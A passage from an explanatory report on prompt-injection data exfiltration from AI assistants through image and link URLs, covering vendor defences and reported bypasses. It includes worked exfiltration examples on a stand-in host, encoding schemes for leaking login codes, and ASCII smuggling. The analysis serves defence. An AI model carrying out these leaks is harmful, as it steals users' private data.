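Microsoft's domain windows.net met all three. Customers of Azure, Microsoft's cloud service, can rent file storage there, and each storage account gets its own name under blob.core.windows.net. Customers can also turn on logging of requests for their files. Rehberger opened a storage account and had ChatGPT put private text into an image address under that account's name. OpenAI's server approved the address because of its domain, the browser sent the request to Microsoft, and Rehberger read the text in his log.

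Allowlists in a Content Security Policy have the same weakness when they include rented storage, as Salesforce's did. For windows.net, the server apparently checked only the domain. Checking the full address should have been an improvement, because the server could see the private text in it.

By 2025, attackers could also steal information from a user's earlier conversations, because ChatGPT had begun to include it in the system prompt, the instructions that a vendor supplies before a chat begins. Rehberger's attack extracted the section on recent conversations. In his video, the attacker's text arrives in a PDF, so a victim who asked for a summary of one document could have details stolen from unrelated chats.

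Rehberger named apache.org, the open-source Apache Software Foundation's domain, as a second accepted site whose logs he could inspect. He had reported these bypasses in October 2024. In the month before he published, he asked OpenAI several times whether it had fixed them but got no update. He left the exact injection text out of his post.

He recommended that OpenAI restrict the accepted domains, publish the list, and let companies manage the check through their own settings. A public list would help attackers look for weak entries, but Rehberger, Imperva and Tenable had all found such entries without one. Customers, meanwhile, had no way of knowing that strangers could rent space on a domain that ChatGPT accepted. Publishing the list would also have made it harder for OpenAI to leave windows.net on it.

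### The tightening of 2025

OpenAI changed the check in the summer of 2025, though sources differ on when and how much it fixed. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025) cites an 11 July message in which OpenAI said it had improved the check's behaviour. Rehberger dates the change to around August and says it stopped the attacks he had demonstrated. He had also noticed that the url_safe query no longer appeared in the browser, which suggests OpenAI had moved the decision to its own servers, as he had advised in 2023.

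The Bing bypass may have kept working for longer. Tenable got several of its attacks to work with GPT-5, which OpenAI released that August, and its screenshots include an attack that used the bypass to load images. Tenable published the attacks in November and said that OpenAI had fixed some of the flaws it had reported.

Radware, another security company, found a stricter rule that autumn. Radware's *ZombieAgent* reports that ChatGPT would open only addresses "exactly as provided" and would not add parameters to them, even when told to. This rule stops the attack in the worked example and would also have stopped Rehberger's use of windows.net.

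An attacker could get around the check by supplying the addresses. Radware emailed the victim a list of complete addresses, which ChatGPT accepted because it did not have to change them. ChatGPT could then leak text by opening them in a particular order. OpenAI did distinguish between sources to some extent, since ChatGPT would not open an attacker's addresses from its stored memories, but it would open addresses from an email.

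Radware reported this on 26 September 2025 and recorded a fix on 16 December, but does not say what the fix was. Six weeks later, OpenAI described a rule under which an address would no longer be accepted just because it appeared in an email, so the fix and the rule may be connected.

### Loading only addresses that are already public

OpenAI set out the new rule on 28 January 2026. The company has a crawler, a program that goes through public web pages and records their addresses in an index, much as a search engine does. When ChatGPT is about to load an address automatically, OpenAI looks for that exact address in the index. ChatGPT loads the address if it is there; otherwise, OpenAI treats it as unverified.

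Rehberger's guess about Bing was close. After reading OpenAI's accompanying paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, he wrote that the company uses its own index.

OpenAI's argument for the rule can be laid out in four steps, of which it leaves the first two mostly unstated:

1. A request leaks a private detail through its address if the address contains that detail.

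2. The model can put the detail into an address only after reading it, so it has to write a new address during the conversation.

3. The crawler finds addresses on the public web and has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.

4. An address in the index therefore existed in public independently of the conversation, and is much less likely to contain the user's private data.

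Because the crawler is separate from the conversations, a failed attempt to load an address does not make later attempts easier. If OpenAI had instead built its index from the addresses ChatGPT tried to open, the attacker's address with "Budget review" in it would have failed the first time, entered the index, and loaded the next time.

OpenAI sensibly wrote "much less likely" in the fourth step, since an attacker who guessed the title could publish an address containing it and wait for the crawler to find it. A private address can also become public by accident, such as when someone posts a shared document's secret link on a forum.

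The first step leaves the largest gap, because the model can also reveal a secret by choosing among public addresses, as in CamoLeak. OpenAI acknowledges this in its paper, according to Embrace The Red. How much can leak this way depends on how many addresses an attacker can get into the index.

Applied to the employee's assistant, the rule would sort addresses like this:

| Address | In the index? | Consequence |
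|---|---|---|
| A photo on a venue's public website, several months old | Probably | Loads automatically |
| `https://pictures.example/pixel.png?title=Budget%20review` | No | Does not load automatically |
| `https://pictures.example/pixel.png` | Yes, if the crawler has found it | Loads, and the log shows a request without the title |
| A photo that a venue posted this morning | Probably not | Unverified, although harmless |
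| A chart on her company's internal website | No, because the crawler cannot log in | Unverified, although harmless |

The last two rows show the drawback of this rule: it checks whether an address is public, which is only a stand-in for whether it contains private data. New pages, internal sites and addresses generated for a single visitor will all fail. OpenAI's post does not give the size of the index or the share of ordinary addresses that fail, so it is hard to judge how often users notice.

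### Why OpenAI rejected a list of trusted sites

OpenAI gives two reasons for not simply allowing a list of well-known websites. Many of these sites have redirects, so an address on a trusted site can lead to the attacker's site. A short list would also produce frequent warnings, because people visit many other sites, and users who see too many warnings learn to dismiss them without reading.

Its own history supports the first reason, since Bing was a trusted site and Tenable used Bing's forwarding links to reach other servers. The index does not stop redirects, but it makes them much less useful to an attacker. Many open redirects take the destination as a parameter. To smuggle out the meeting title, an attacker would have the model write it into that parameter, which would create an address the crawler had never seen. A fixed forwarding link in the index could still lead to the attacker's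 server, but it would carry the same text for every user.

The index also protects against leaks through rented storage. The old rule accepted any address under windows.net. The new rule lets a public file there load but blocks an address to which the model has added the user's chat history, regardless of who owns the domain or can read the logs. A vendor no longer has to examine every service on a permitted host.

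OpenAI's case is weaker on warnings. An index of the public web surely covers more harmless addresses than a list of popular sites does, particularly addresses on small sites. But the new rule also produces warnings, and without figures there is no way to tell whether they are rare enough for people to keep reading them.

### What happens to an unverified address

When an address is not in the index, ChatGPT can look for another source or let the user decide. The user sees a dialog titled "Check this link is safe", which displays the address and lets them copy or open it. If the address looks suspicious, OpenAI advises users not to open it and to ask ChatGPT for a different source or a summary. The post does not describe what appears in place of an unverified image.

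Looking for another source is usually safer than showing the dialog, because nobody has to recognise encoded data in a long address. If ChatGPT can't open one page about a venue, another will often do. The dialog is more useful when the address that fails the check is harmless, such as a link to the employee's internal site, which she will probably recognise.

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) calls the mechanism Safe Url and describes it a little differently. Safe Url is meant to detect when something the assistant learned in the conversation would be sent to a third party, and the user is then shown that information. An index lookup alone cannot do this, because it can show that an address is unfamiliar but not whether the unfamiliar part is a meeting title or a meaningless file number. Either OpenAI combines the lookup with some other analysis, or the post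 describes the purpose of the check more than how it works.

In the same post, OpenAI says that most of the attacks it knows of fail earlier because its safety training leads the model to refuse, and that cases that reach Safe Url are rare. But its example is an email, reported by outside researchers in 2025, that led ChatGPT to submit an employee's details to an outside address in 50% of tests when the user asked for detailed research on that day's emails. OpenAI concludes that companies should limit what a deceived assistant can do, as they limit the refunds a customer service worker can give.

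By March 2026 OpenAI had extended Safe Url beyond the chat window:

| Product | What Safe Url covers |
|---|---|
| Atlas, OpenAI's web browser | Opening pages and saving bookmarks |
| Deep Research, which reads many sources and writes a report | Searches and opening pages |

OpenAI does not explain why it included bookmarks. A deceived agent could presumably save a bookmark with private data in its address, and the user would send out that data by opening it days later. Searches pose a similar risk because the search terms can contain a secret.

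Each new feature needs the check, however, and Embrace The Red describes the last practical risk as some of OpenAI's developers not knowing the check exists, or not using it in what they build. Rehberger had worked on the same problem inside other companies, and it occurred at OpenAI when some ChatGPT apps did not use url_safe.

### ChatGPhish: fixed images in page summaries

In May 2026, four months after OpenAI published the new rule, Permiso found that ChatGPT loaded images from pages it summarised. Permiso's *ChatGPhish* describes tests with Firefox, which can send the page a user is reading to a chatbot for a summary.

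The researchers added instructions to a GitHub README, asking for a normal summary followed by a fake security alert. When they had ChatGPT summarise the page, it produced both. The alert contained a link in one version and a QR code in another, with the code's image hosted on Amazon storage that the researchers had rented. A person who scans the code opens the address on a phone, where protections on the computer don't apply. The researchers got the same results from their own ordinary web page, so the problem did not depend on GitHub.

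A third version loaded an image through a link-shortening service. The researchers' server recorded the requester's IP address, the browser's user-agent string, the exact time and, if the browser sent it, the page the request came from. Permiso says that together these can confirm that a particular person read a particular page through ChatGPT. This works best if the attacker gives each target a different page, because an IP address alone may not identify anyone.

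None of this breaks the guarantee OpenAI gave in January, because that guarantee covers user-specific data in the address itself, and the researchers' images had the same addresses for every reader. The network address and the time came from the request itself, and a rule about the text of an address can't hide them once it allows the request. OpenAI had also said that the check does not make a page's content trustworthy, so the fake alert doesn't break the guarantee either.

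The guarantee is narrower than many users would assume, though. A proxy could have covered part of the difference, because proxies and address checks protect different things:

| Defence | Meeting title in the address | User's network address | Time of the request |
|---|---|---|---|
| Neither | Leaks | Leaks | Leaks |
| Proxy that fetches any address | Leaks | Hidden | Leaks |
| Address check alone | Blocked | Leaks if the address passes | Leaks if the address passes |
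| Address check, then proxy | Blocked | Hidden | Leaks if the address passes and the proxy has no copy |

It is less clear why the images loaded. A crawler seems unlikely to have already found a new QR code in rented storage. The README was public, so the crawler may have recorded the image addresses before the test, but Permiso does not say how long they had been online. OpenAI also may not have applied the check to these summaries.

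Another explanation seems more likely, though it is an inference that neither OpenAI nor Permiso has confirmed. As Rehberger understands it, ChatGPT treats any address in the user's own message as safe for the rest of the chat, and Imperva had found the same in an earlier version. According to Mozilla's *Access AI chatbots in Firefox*, the "Summarize Page" option sends the chatbot the page's content and title along with the prompt. If ChatGPT receives the content, title and prompt as one message from the user, every address on the attacker's page may count as typed by the user.

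If the inference is right, an attacker could leak text as well as phish. To leak text by having the model choose among prepared addresses, the attacker would only need to list them on the page, without getting them into OpenAI's index. OpenAI could prevent this by treating only what the user typed as the user's and the page as outside material, but Firefox would have to mark the boundary between them.

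Permiso reported the problem to OpenAI on 29 April through Bugcrowd, a service that handles such reports for companies. The next day OpenAI replied that it could not reproduce the problem from the details given. Permiso sent a fuller report on 1 May, with screenshots and clearer steps. This was first marked "Not Applicable" and later marked as a duplicate of someone else's earlier report. On 7 May Permiso asked to discuss the wider effects further, including the QR codes and the tracking. It published its findings on 29 May, and its timeline does not record a fix.

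## How much can leak through approved addresses

OpenAI's index of public pages keeps ChatGPT from automatically loading an address the model has just made up, but the model can still leak a secret by choosing among approved addresses, as in CamoLeak. How much can leak depends mainly on how many addresses the attacker has prepared and how many requests get through, so it can be calculated.

### The choice of address as a message

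Suppose the attacker has two ordinary pictures on pictures.example, and both are in the index. In the hidden text on the page about conference venues, the attacker tells the assistant to show the first picture if the employee is meeting a certain client next week, and the second if she is not. Either address would pass a check, but the attacker can still tell from the log entry whether she is meeting the client.

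A choice between two equally likely options carries one bit of information. A choice among N carries the base-2 logarithm of N:

```
information per request = log2(N) bits
```

| Prepared addresses (N) | Bits per request |
|---|---|
| 2 | 1.0 |
| 10 | 3.3 |
| 36 (one for each letter and digit) | 5.2 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 |

Doubling the number of addresses adds only one bit, so 1,000 addresses carry about twice as much per request as 36 do.

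A six-digit login code is a useful test because it is short and valuable, and SearchLeak showed that email titles can contain one. There are a million possible codes, which makes 19.9 bits. (That is a hair under the 20 bits that Cornucopia's *Out of Band Verifier*, part of a security checklist for developers, requires of such codes, though the same item accepts six random digits as typically sufficient.)

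With ten addresses, one for each digit, the model can spell out the code in six requests. An attacker who treats the code as a single number needs fewer. If the requests arrive in order, k requests chosen from N addresses can form N^k different sequences, and the attacker needs at least a million:

```
36^3    =    46,656    too few
36^4    = 1,679,616    enough: four requests
1,000^2 = 1,000,000    exactly enough: two requests
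```

The code 482913, written in base 36, is "acm9", so the model would load the pictures for a, c, m and 9. With 1,000 pictures numbered from 000 to 999, it would load picture 482 and then picture 913, without having to do any arithmetic.

These figures apply if the model follows the injected text without mistakes. The method suits short secrets, because a 500-character email would take about 500 requests if the model spelled it out letter by letter.

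### Lost order and missing repeats

A browser fetches several images at once, so the requests can reach the attacker's server out of order. Caching may also keep repeated pictures out of the log, as in CamoLeak. If the model spelled out the code 774201 with one picture per digit, the log might show 0, 7, 2, 1 and 4, which fits many codes.

An attacker can design the list so that neither problem matters. Twenty pictures are enough for any six-digit code if each stands for one binary digit and the reply includes it only when that digit is 1, because 2^20 is 1,048,576. In binary, 482913 is 01110101111001100001, which contains eleven 1s. The reply would load eleven pictures once each, and the attacker could read the code whatever order they arrived in.

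Another method is easier for the model because it avoids binary, but it needs more pictures. The attacker prepares 60 pictures, one for each digit in each of the six positions, so that one picture means "4 in first place" and another means "4 in fifth place". The model can then leak the whole code in six requests, again in any order and without requesting any picture twice.

### The test with 36 images

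Rehberger tried the basic method on the day OpenAI's address check appeared in December 2023. According to Embrace The Red, he tested an image address on his own site for each letter and digit, and nine of the 36 passed the check and loaded. He demonstrated the leak by sending the word "hi" as two requests. He thought the method was slow and could leak only small amounts of data. He also thought users might notice it, and that OpenAI might too if it monitored the queries to its check.

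Blocking 27 of 36 addresses limits an attacker who spells out words to those made of the nine remaining characters. It is much less effective against an attacker who assigns new meanings to the nine working addresses. Each request then carries 3.2 bits, so seven requests in order are enough to send a login code, compared with four when all 36 addresses work. Losing the order of the requests would limit the attacker more, because nine images that are each either present or absent have only 512 combinations.

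Others later got a full alphabet of addresses past the check. Imperva put a fixed address for each character in text that ChatGPT treated as the user's, then reconstructed the secret from the order of the requests. It also considered buying a separate domain for each character, at a dollar or two apiece, because the check accepted bare domains. Tenable got one page for each letter into Bing's index and had ChatGPT display the matching Bing links in sequence. Imperva still concluded that extracting large volumes without detection had become significantly harder, which is consistent with each request leaking only one character.

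After OpenAI published its stricter rule, Rehberger wrote on Embrace The Red that the trick still applies if the attacker's addresses are in OpenAI's index. He noted that anyone with a fairly large website or blog probably already has 36 indexed addresses. An attacker could also use thousands and explain in the injected text what each one means. With an address for every common word, leaking the meeting title "Budget review" would take two requests instead of thirteen. He was reasoning from the rule and had not tested the feature recently, so he did not demonstrate a bypass.

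### Comparing the proposed limits

In 2023 Rehberger suggested that OpenAI allow only one image per reply, or a handful at most. In 2026 he added two related ideas. ChatGPT could keep each response for a few minutes, so that loading the same address again sends nothing, or it could refuse to visit the same full address twice in a session. For a login code, the limits compare as follows:

| Limit | With 36 addresses | With 1,000 addresses |
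|---|---|---|
| None | 4 requests | 2 requests |
| No repeats, order visible | 4 requests | 2 requests |
| No repeats, order lost | Up to 6 requests | Up to 3 requests |
| One image per reply | 4 replies | 2 replies |
| One image per reply and no repeats | 4 replies | 2 replies |

Stopping repeated requests, by caching or refusing them, does almost nothing to protect a six-digit code. Four different addresses chosen from 36 can form 1,413,720 ordered sequences, more than the million possible codes. With 1,000 addresses, each standing for three digits, a code such as 427427 would need the same image twice. The attacker would see only one request and could infer that the two halves were identical.

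A ban on repeats does limit the total that a session can leak. If the attacker has 36 addresses and can use each only once, the session can leak about 138 bits (just under seven login codes) when the order is visible, and 36 bits when it is not. To raise that limit, the attacker has to get more addresses into the index.

A cap on images per reply slows the leak but doesn't limit the total. Each reply can leak 5.2 bits through one image chosen from 36, for as long as the conversation continues and the model keeps following the attacker's text. Samoilenko's 2023 attack, for example, affected every later answer. The cap also helps the attacker, because requests sent a reply apart arrive in the right order. The delay gives some protection to login codes sent to a user's device, which NIST, the US standards institute, describes as short-lived secrets, but two replies may take less than a minute.

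A cap on the whole conversation would be much stronger. One image chosen from 1,000 would give the attacker three of the six digits and leave 1,000 possible codes. On a website that allows five guesses, the attacker would then have a 0.5% chance of getting in.

It also matters whether the user's request or an injected instruction uses the allowance first. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) gives a formal example of an agent that may send one message per run. An injected instruction uses that message to send a password reset code, so the agent cannot send the message the user wanted. In a second example, the agent sends the user's message before it reads any untrusted text, so every injected message fails. A chat product could copy the second example by choosing its pictures before the model reads anything private.

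Users would barely notice a ban on repeat requests, because the app can show its stored copy of a picture. A cap of one image would spoil the employee's comparison of three conference venues and do little to stop a determined attacker. Caching is therefore worth having, but a small cap is harder to justify in a product that people use to look at pictures.

### ZombieAgent and numbered addresses

Radware's ZombieAgent attack used the same idea against ChatGPT's tool for opening links. It emailed the victim a complete address for every character, which got around OpenAI's ban on adding data to addresses. Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* traces that ban to ShadowLeak, an earlier Radware attack that took data from Gmail.

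Radware numbered the addresses to keep the characters in order, so the letter "a" had ten, from a0 to a9. A block of ten characters needs 360 addresses. This is a larger version of the scheme with 60 pictures, and neither caching nor a ban on repeats would stop it. Radware also got a version with markdown images to work in the chat display, but found it less reliable and easier to block.

According to *ChatGPT falls to new data pilfering attack* (2026), OpenAI responded by stopping ChatGPT from opening a link from an email unless the link appears in a well-known public index or the user supplied it in the chat. This is essentially the rule OpenAI explained in January. An attacker can no longer list 360 new addresses in an email and use them the same day, but 360 addresses already in the index would carry just as much information.

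Anthropic had a similar problem with the tool that lets Claude open web pages. Willison (2026) recounts that the tool accepted exact addresses from the user or search results, and any link on a page it had already opened. In July 2026 Ayush Paul showed that a website could use this to get Claude to spell out a user's name, employer and home city by following one link per letter. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links it found on fetched pages.

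In *The Read-Only Lie*, the blogger dyb calculates that each page offered 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen, so each choice carried 4.75 bits. Thirty characters make about 143 bits. Each address was one character longer than the last, so no address repeated and their lengths showed the order. A cap on the number of fetches would have limited this attack more than caching. Developers who use Claude's tool in their own software can set one, and Willison's example allows five fetches. The first fetch loads the first page, which leaves four choices, or 19 bits, slightly less than a six-digit login code. With 32 links on each page, four choices would carry 20 bits, which is enough for the code.

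### Splitting a secret over several requests

An attacker can also split a secret into pieces and put each piece in a separate address. An exact-address rule would block this because the addresses are new, but the attack shows how well a model handles a leak in several steps. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested it in *Silent Egress* with an agent built on qwen2.5:7b, a small open model they ran on their own equipment. They put an invented secret in the model's context and asked the agent to summarise a web page containing malicious instructions.

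The researchers put the instructions in one of four places: the page's title, its description, its main text or the text of a link. The agent reached the page either directly or through redirects, and the instructions were to send the secret either whole or in four pieces. The researchers tested each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs. In 120 further runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the attacker's server.

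| Result | Whole secret | Four pieces |
|---|---|---|
| Agent contacted the attacker's server | 238 of 240 runs | 185 of 240 runs |
| First request contained sensitive data | 96.7% | 26.3% |

The figures do not quite support Lan and colleagues' claim that the second row shows splitting makes a leak harder to detect. Their measure counts any fragment of the secret, so the low rate could also mean that the model often sent pieces with nothing useful in them. They also report that sensitive data appeared in the first request in 26.3% of runs but in the first three requests in only 15.8%, which is impossible under their own definition. The main results do not include how often all four pieces arrived.

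The first row is more reliable. Success fell from 99% to 77% when the instructions became longer and required several steps, so an attack that needs many requests fails more often. A chat display may make such an attack easier, since the model can write all the image addresses in one reply instead of keeping track of pieces across separate tool calls. The percentages should not be applied to commercial products, because the model was small, its system prompt was minimal, and the secret was in plain view.

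The study also tested defences, with 30 runs for each, but only against attacks that sent the whole secret at once. Telling the model to ignore instructions in web content reduced leaks from 100% to 66.7%, and marking the content as untrusted data had no effect. An allowlist of domains stopped every leak, though the attacker's domain was deliberately one that no sensible list would include. A filter for random-looking text also stopped every leak, but it examined only values longer than ten characters, so the four-character pieces in the paper's own example would have passed. Such a filter has even less to detect when the attacker uses approved addresses, because a request for `/a.png` looks the same whether or not it stands for a letter of a secret.

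Lan and colleagues recommend looking at requests together and limiting their number per session. A vendor could apply both to images. Thirty requests for tiny pictures on one unfamiliar site are suspicious even if each is harmless. But a page of product thumbnails can look similar, and a leak that takes only two requests would not stand out.

### What a destination allowlist can promise

Rahman and Kim tested a wider set of defences in *The Framing Gap*. They gave an invented secret to agents based on six models. Each agent read one web page and then took one action, which could be to send data to an address. They counted an attack as successful only if the agent kept the secret after reading a clean page and leaked it after reading the altered one. GPT-4o, a 2024 model, resisted all ten types of plainly worded attack, but it leaked the secret in 40% of trials when the page disguised it,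 for example as a required checksum or a routine setting.

For the comparison of defences they used an agent built on Llama 3.1 8B, a small open model:

| Defence | Leaks under reworded attacks |
|---|---|
| None | 21.2% |
| Separate input channel for outside text | 38.8% |
| SecAlign, a model trained to resist injection | 32.5% |
| One model plans, another reads the page | 0% |
| Allowlist of destinations | 0% by definition |

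Rahman and Kim do not rank the first three rows because each figure comes from a single run, and two identical tests on GPT-4o gave 31.9% and 40.0%. In a separate test, a filter that decoded outgoing text caught every encoding it was designed to handle but missed ROT13, a simple letter substitution, every time.

Rahman and Kim acknowledge that the allowlist was certain to score zero leaks, because it blocks any message to an untrusted host and the study counts a leak only when the secret goes to such a host. They add that splitting a secret over several calls cannot defeat an allowlist. This also follows from the definition of a leak, and the study could not test it because their agent took only one step.

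In a chat display, this guarantee holds only if attackers cannot find out what the permitted hosts receive. Bing and Microsoft's rented storage did not meet that condition. The guarantee also doesn't extend to OpenAI's index, which is a list of public addresses and can include pages on an attacker's own server. Even a list of trustworthy hosts can leak information to an attacker who can observe the agent's steps. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* gives the example of an instruction to fetch a permitted newsletter if a secret is 0 and a forbidden address otherwise. The attacker can tell whether the secret is 0 by seeing whether the request was allowed.

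Separating the two models removes the cause of the leak, because the model that reads the attacker's page never has the secret. In the study, nine out of ten page summaries were still usable with this separation. One model could summarise the page about venues and choose its pictures without access to the employee's inbox, while another looked up her dates. The app would then combine the two answers without showing either model the other's text. The hidden passage could still add a picture to the summary, but it could not make the choice of picture depend on "Budget review". This would be less convenient for the employee, because the first model could not leave out venues that are closed on her dates.

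## Links that leak only when clicked

Vendors are more lenient with links than with images, partly because a link normally leaks nothing until the user clicks it. Chat products also need links, because people check an assistant's answers by opening its sources and a search result is of little use without a link. Microsoft nonetheless lists clickable links, along with images, among the known ways to exfiltrate data.

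Suppose the hidden text on the page about conference venues asks for a link instead of a picture:

```
[Compare the three venues](https://pictures.example/?title=Budget%20review)
```

The employee sees only the underlined words "Compare the three venues". On a computer, she can rest the pointer on them to see the address in a corner of the browser window. Few people do this for every link, and a phone has no pointer. A single click can also leak a lot of data, because an address can be thousands of characters long.

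### Slack AI: a private key behind an error message

In August 2024 the security company PromptArmor showed how well a label can hide an address. Slack is a messaging app for workplaces, and Slack AI answers questions about the messages in it. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* describes the attack:

1. A developer keeps an API key, a password for use by programs, in a private channel that only she can read.

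2. The attacker, who has an account in the same Slack workspace, creates a public channel with no other members and posts instructions there.

3. The developer asks Slack AI for her key. It searches her private channels and every public channel, including those she never joined, and gives the model both messages.

4. The model follows the attacker's message. It replies that the message failed to load and offers a link labelled "click here to reauthenticate", with the key in the link's address.

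The attacker could not read the private channel and did not need to know what was in it. The label also gave the developer a believable reason to click, since people often have to log in again.

Slack AI's citations did not expose the attack. The attacker's message had shaped the reply, but Slack AI cited only the developer's own private channel. The message was also missing from the first page of search results. In a second test, with an ordinary phishing link, Slack AI did cite the attacker's channel. PromptArmor concluded that the citations depended partly on chance.

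PromptArmor reported the flaw on 14 August. Slack asked questions over the next two days, and on 19 August it called the evidence insufficient, saying that anyone in a workspace can search public channels and that this is "intended behavior". This applied to the attacker's message, but not to the key, which came from a private channel. Willison (2024) took the reply as a sign that Slack did not yet understand the problem.

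PromptArmor published its findings on 20 August, and Slack deployed a patch the same day. Slack (2024) said that someone with an account in the same workspace could phish users for certain data "under very limited and specific circumstances", and that it had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data. It did not say whether the patch changed the search, the model's instructions or the display of links.

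Needing an account may also have been less of a barrier than Slack implied. On the day of PromptArmor's report, Slack AI began using uploaded files as well as messages. An outsider could then have hidden instructions in a PDF and waited for an employee to upload it. PromptArmor had finished testing before this change, but thought the attack very likely to work.

### Five ways to treat a link

Vendors have several options between leaving a link alone and deleting it. For the link to the venue comparison, they work out as follows:

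| Treatment | What the employee sees | What still leaks |
|---|---|---|
| Plain text | The label, or an address she cannot click | Nothing, unless she copies the address into a browser |
| Full address on display | The label with the whole address beside it | The title, if she clicks anyway |
| Confirmation page | A page that asks whether to continue | The title, if she continues or the host is exempt |
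| Reputation check | A normal link, unless the site has a bad record | The title, if the site is new or well regarded |
| Removal of unknown addresses | A notice, or the label without a link | Only her choice among the links that remain |

### Plain text

Showing links as unclickable text is the strongest protection that leaves the words of the answer intact. Rehberger advised Microsoft that Copilot should ideally not render hyperlinks at all. The app should remove the address and keep only the label, because an attacker can use the model's answer to get the user to copy a printed address into a browser. Other software may also make the address clickable again, for instance when the user pastes the answer into an email.

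Restricting links makes citations less useful, but an app can avoid much of this problem by writing the citation links itself. The model would write only a source's number, and ordinary software would attach the address from its record of the pages the model had read. The employee could still open the venues' websites, but the model couldn't add "Budget review" to an address.

### Showing the full address, and characters that do not show

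If Slack AI had printed the address next to "click here to reauthenticate", the developer might have recognised her own key in it. PromptArmor's screenshots show that the key is readable in the address when the pointer rests on the link. An attacker can make the data harder to recognise by having the model encode it, and in early 2024 Rehberger found a way to make it invisible.

Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* describes an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that started with instructions in an email or shared document. When the user asked Copilot about the email or document, Copilot searched her mailbox, without asking, for another message, such as one containing Slack login codes. It then wrote that message's contents into a link using Unicode tags.

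Unicode is the standard that gives every character a number. Its tag characters are a second set of the basic letters, digits and punctuation marks that most programs do not display. Each has the number of the ordinary character plus a fixed amount:

| Letter | Ordinary number | Tag number | What the browser sends for the tag |
|---|---|---|---|
| B | U+0042 | U+E0042 | `%F3%A0%81%82` |
| u | U+0075 | U+E0075 | `%F3%A0%81%B5` |

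Copilot could therefore display an address that looked short and complete but had an email's contents hidden at the end. Rehberger calls the technique ASCII smuggling, after the basic character set. His instructions included an encoded example to show Copilot how to do it.

A careful user could still have noticed something odd, since Rehberger notes that a link of this kind looks wrong when the pointer rests on it. The browser encodes each tag as twelve visible characters before sending it, so the thirteen characters of "Budget review" become 156. An app that displays addresses should therefore show this encoded form or reject any address that contains tags. Rejecting them would affect very few legitimate links, because tags have almost no everyday use apart from a few flag emoji.

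Rehberger reported the invisible characters to Microsoft on 17 January 2024, and Microsoft closed the report the next day as low severity. Microsoft opened a case in February, after he sent a full attack that extracted sales figures. In April it asked for time until the end of May. On 2 July Rehberger noted that his attack had stopped working, and he published it in late August.

Microsoft didn't answer when he asked how it had fixed the flaw, but Copilot appeared to have stopped rendering links some months earlier. This is consistent with the link filter that EchoLeak bypassed in January 2025. If that filter was the fix, Microsoft dealt with invisible characters by removing the links that contained them.

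### Google Colab's confirmation page

A confirmation page appears after the user clicks a link, when she has already shown that she wants to open it. OpenAI's link warning works this way, and Google used an older page of this kind in Colab, its service for writing and running code in shared documents called notebooks. Colab has an assistant based on Gemini.

Rehberger had reported an image leak in that assistant in November 2023, and Google closed the report as fixed in January. At that point an attacker had to get the user to paste in malicious text. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) explains that links then became more important because Colab began to put the notebook's contents into the prompt automatically, which let anyone who shared a notebook include instructions for the assistant.

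Colab puts a google.com address in front of every link in the assistant's replies. For the link to the venue comparison, the result would be:

```
https://www.google.com/url?q=
    https%3A%2F%2Fpictures.example%2F%3Ftitle%3DBudget%2520review
```

Clicking the link opens a Google confirmation page before the browser continues to the address after `q=`. If the employee turns back there, pictures.example receives nothing.

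Rehberger found in tests that Google skipped the confirmation page for links to its own domains. A link to a Google Meet video call opened at once, which could put a user in a call with a scammer. Links to Apps Script, which Rehberger had used to collect data from Bard in 2023, also opened without the confirmation page.

He combined this with instructions that made the assistant talk like a pirate and ask the user for personal information. The assistant put the answers and the notebook's source code into a link labelled "I'm feeling lucky", which pointed to his own Apps Script program. When he clicked the link, his log received the name, email address and code. The results of running the code did not leak, because Colab did not include them in the prompt.

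Google could have closed this gap by exempting only hosts where outsiders cannot run programs, or by exempting none. Showing the page for every link would have been safer but would have interrupted many harmless visits to Google's own documentation.

One advantage of a confirmation page over a warning in the chat is that ordinary software writes it, so an attacker's text cannot change the wording. But the attacker controls the address shown on the page and can make it very long. Checkmarx's *Turning AI Safeguards Into Weapons with HITL Dialog Forging* shows a similar trick with the dialogs in which coding assistants ask permission to run a command, where harmless-looking text before and after the dangerous part pushes it out of view. A page that shortens long addresses to fit the screen could also hide the meeting title.

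### Why a reputation check misses a new domain

Checkmarx pointed out that a new domain passes checks by a reputation service such as Google's Safe Browsing, which can list a dangerous site only after someone has discovered it. If the attacker registers pictures.example on Monday and the employee clicks on Tuesday, a listing on Friday would protect later users, but the attacker would already have her meeting title.

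Reputation services may never list the site as dangerous, because they look mainly for malicious software and fake login pages. A server that collects data from URLs needs neither. It can return a blank page or a real comparison of conference venues. An inspector who visited it without the stolen data in the URL would see nothing wrong.

A vendor could treat every recently registered domain as suspicious. This would catch attackers who make the least effort, but it would also flag new businesses. It would miss attackers who bought an old domain, as Noma did with Salesforce's, or rented space on a respected host. Colab's exemption for Google's domains also relied on reputation, and it let Apps Script through.

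The check is still worthwhile protection against known phishing sites, which cause harm whether or not the address contains private data.

### Removing addresses the assistant made up

To stop the model from adding data to an address, a vendor has to reject any address that is not already on an approved list or in a trusted source. Salesforce's Trusted URLs feature works this way. In the worked example, the employee would see a notice or a bare label instead of the link.

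The choice among approved addresses can still leak data, but much less through links than through images, because a reply can load dozens of images while a click normally opens one link. Even with 1,000 approved links, an attacker would need two clicks to get a six-digit login code. Allowing only approved addresses therefore protects links fairly well, even though it leaves a slow leak through images, as long as the approved sites do not record the rest of the address for an attacker.

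It does nothing against phishing, because a fraudulent site can have a fixed public address. Permiso criticised ChatGPT for displaying links from a summarised page without labelling their source. A label such as "from the page you are reading" would help the employee judge a fake security alert. It would not appear on a link that the assistant composed, which is the kind most likely to contain her data. An app would need to label that link differently or remove it.

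### Whether people notice

Two of the five treatments, displaying the address and asking for confirmation, rely on the user to spot the problem. No published study appears to have tested whether people notice private data in a chatbot's links or heed warnings about those links. Research on related questions gives little reason to expect that they do.

Li, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Are You Sure?*, had 303 people work with simulated assistants that an attacker had compromised. Each person completed three everyday or professional tasks, such as answering email or choosing a job candidate, with one of three kinds of warning:

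| Warning | Participants who noticed anything unusual |
|---|---|
| A notice at the start | 8.6% |
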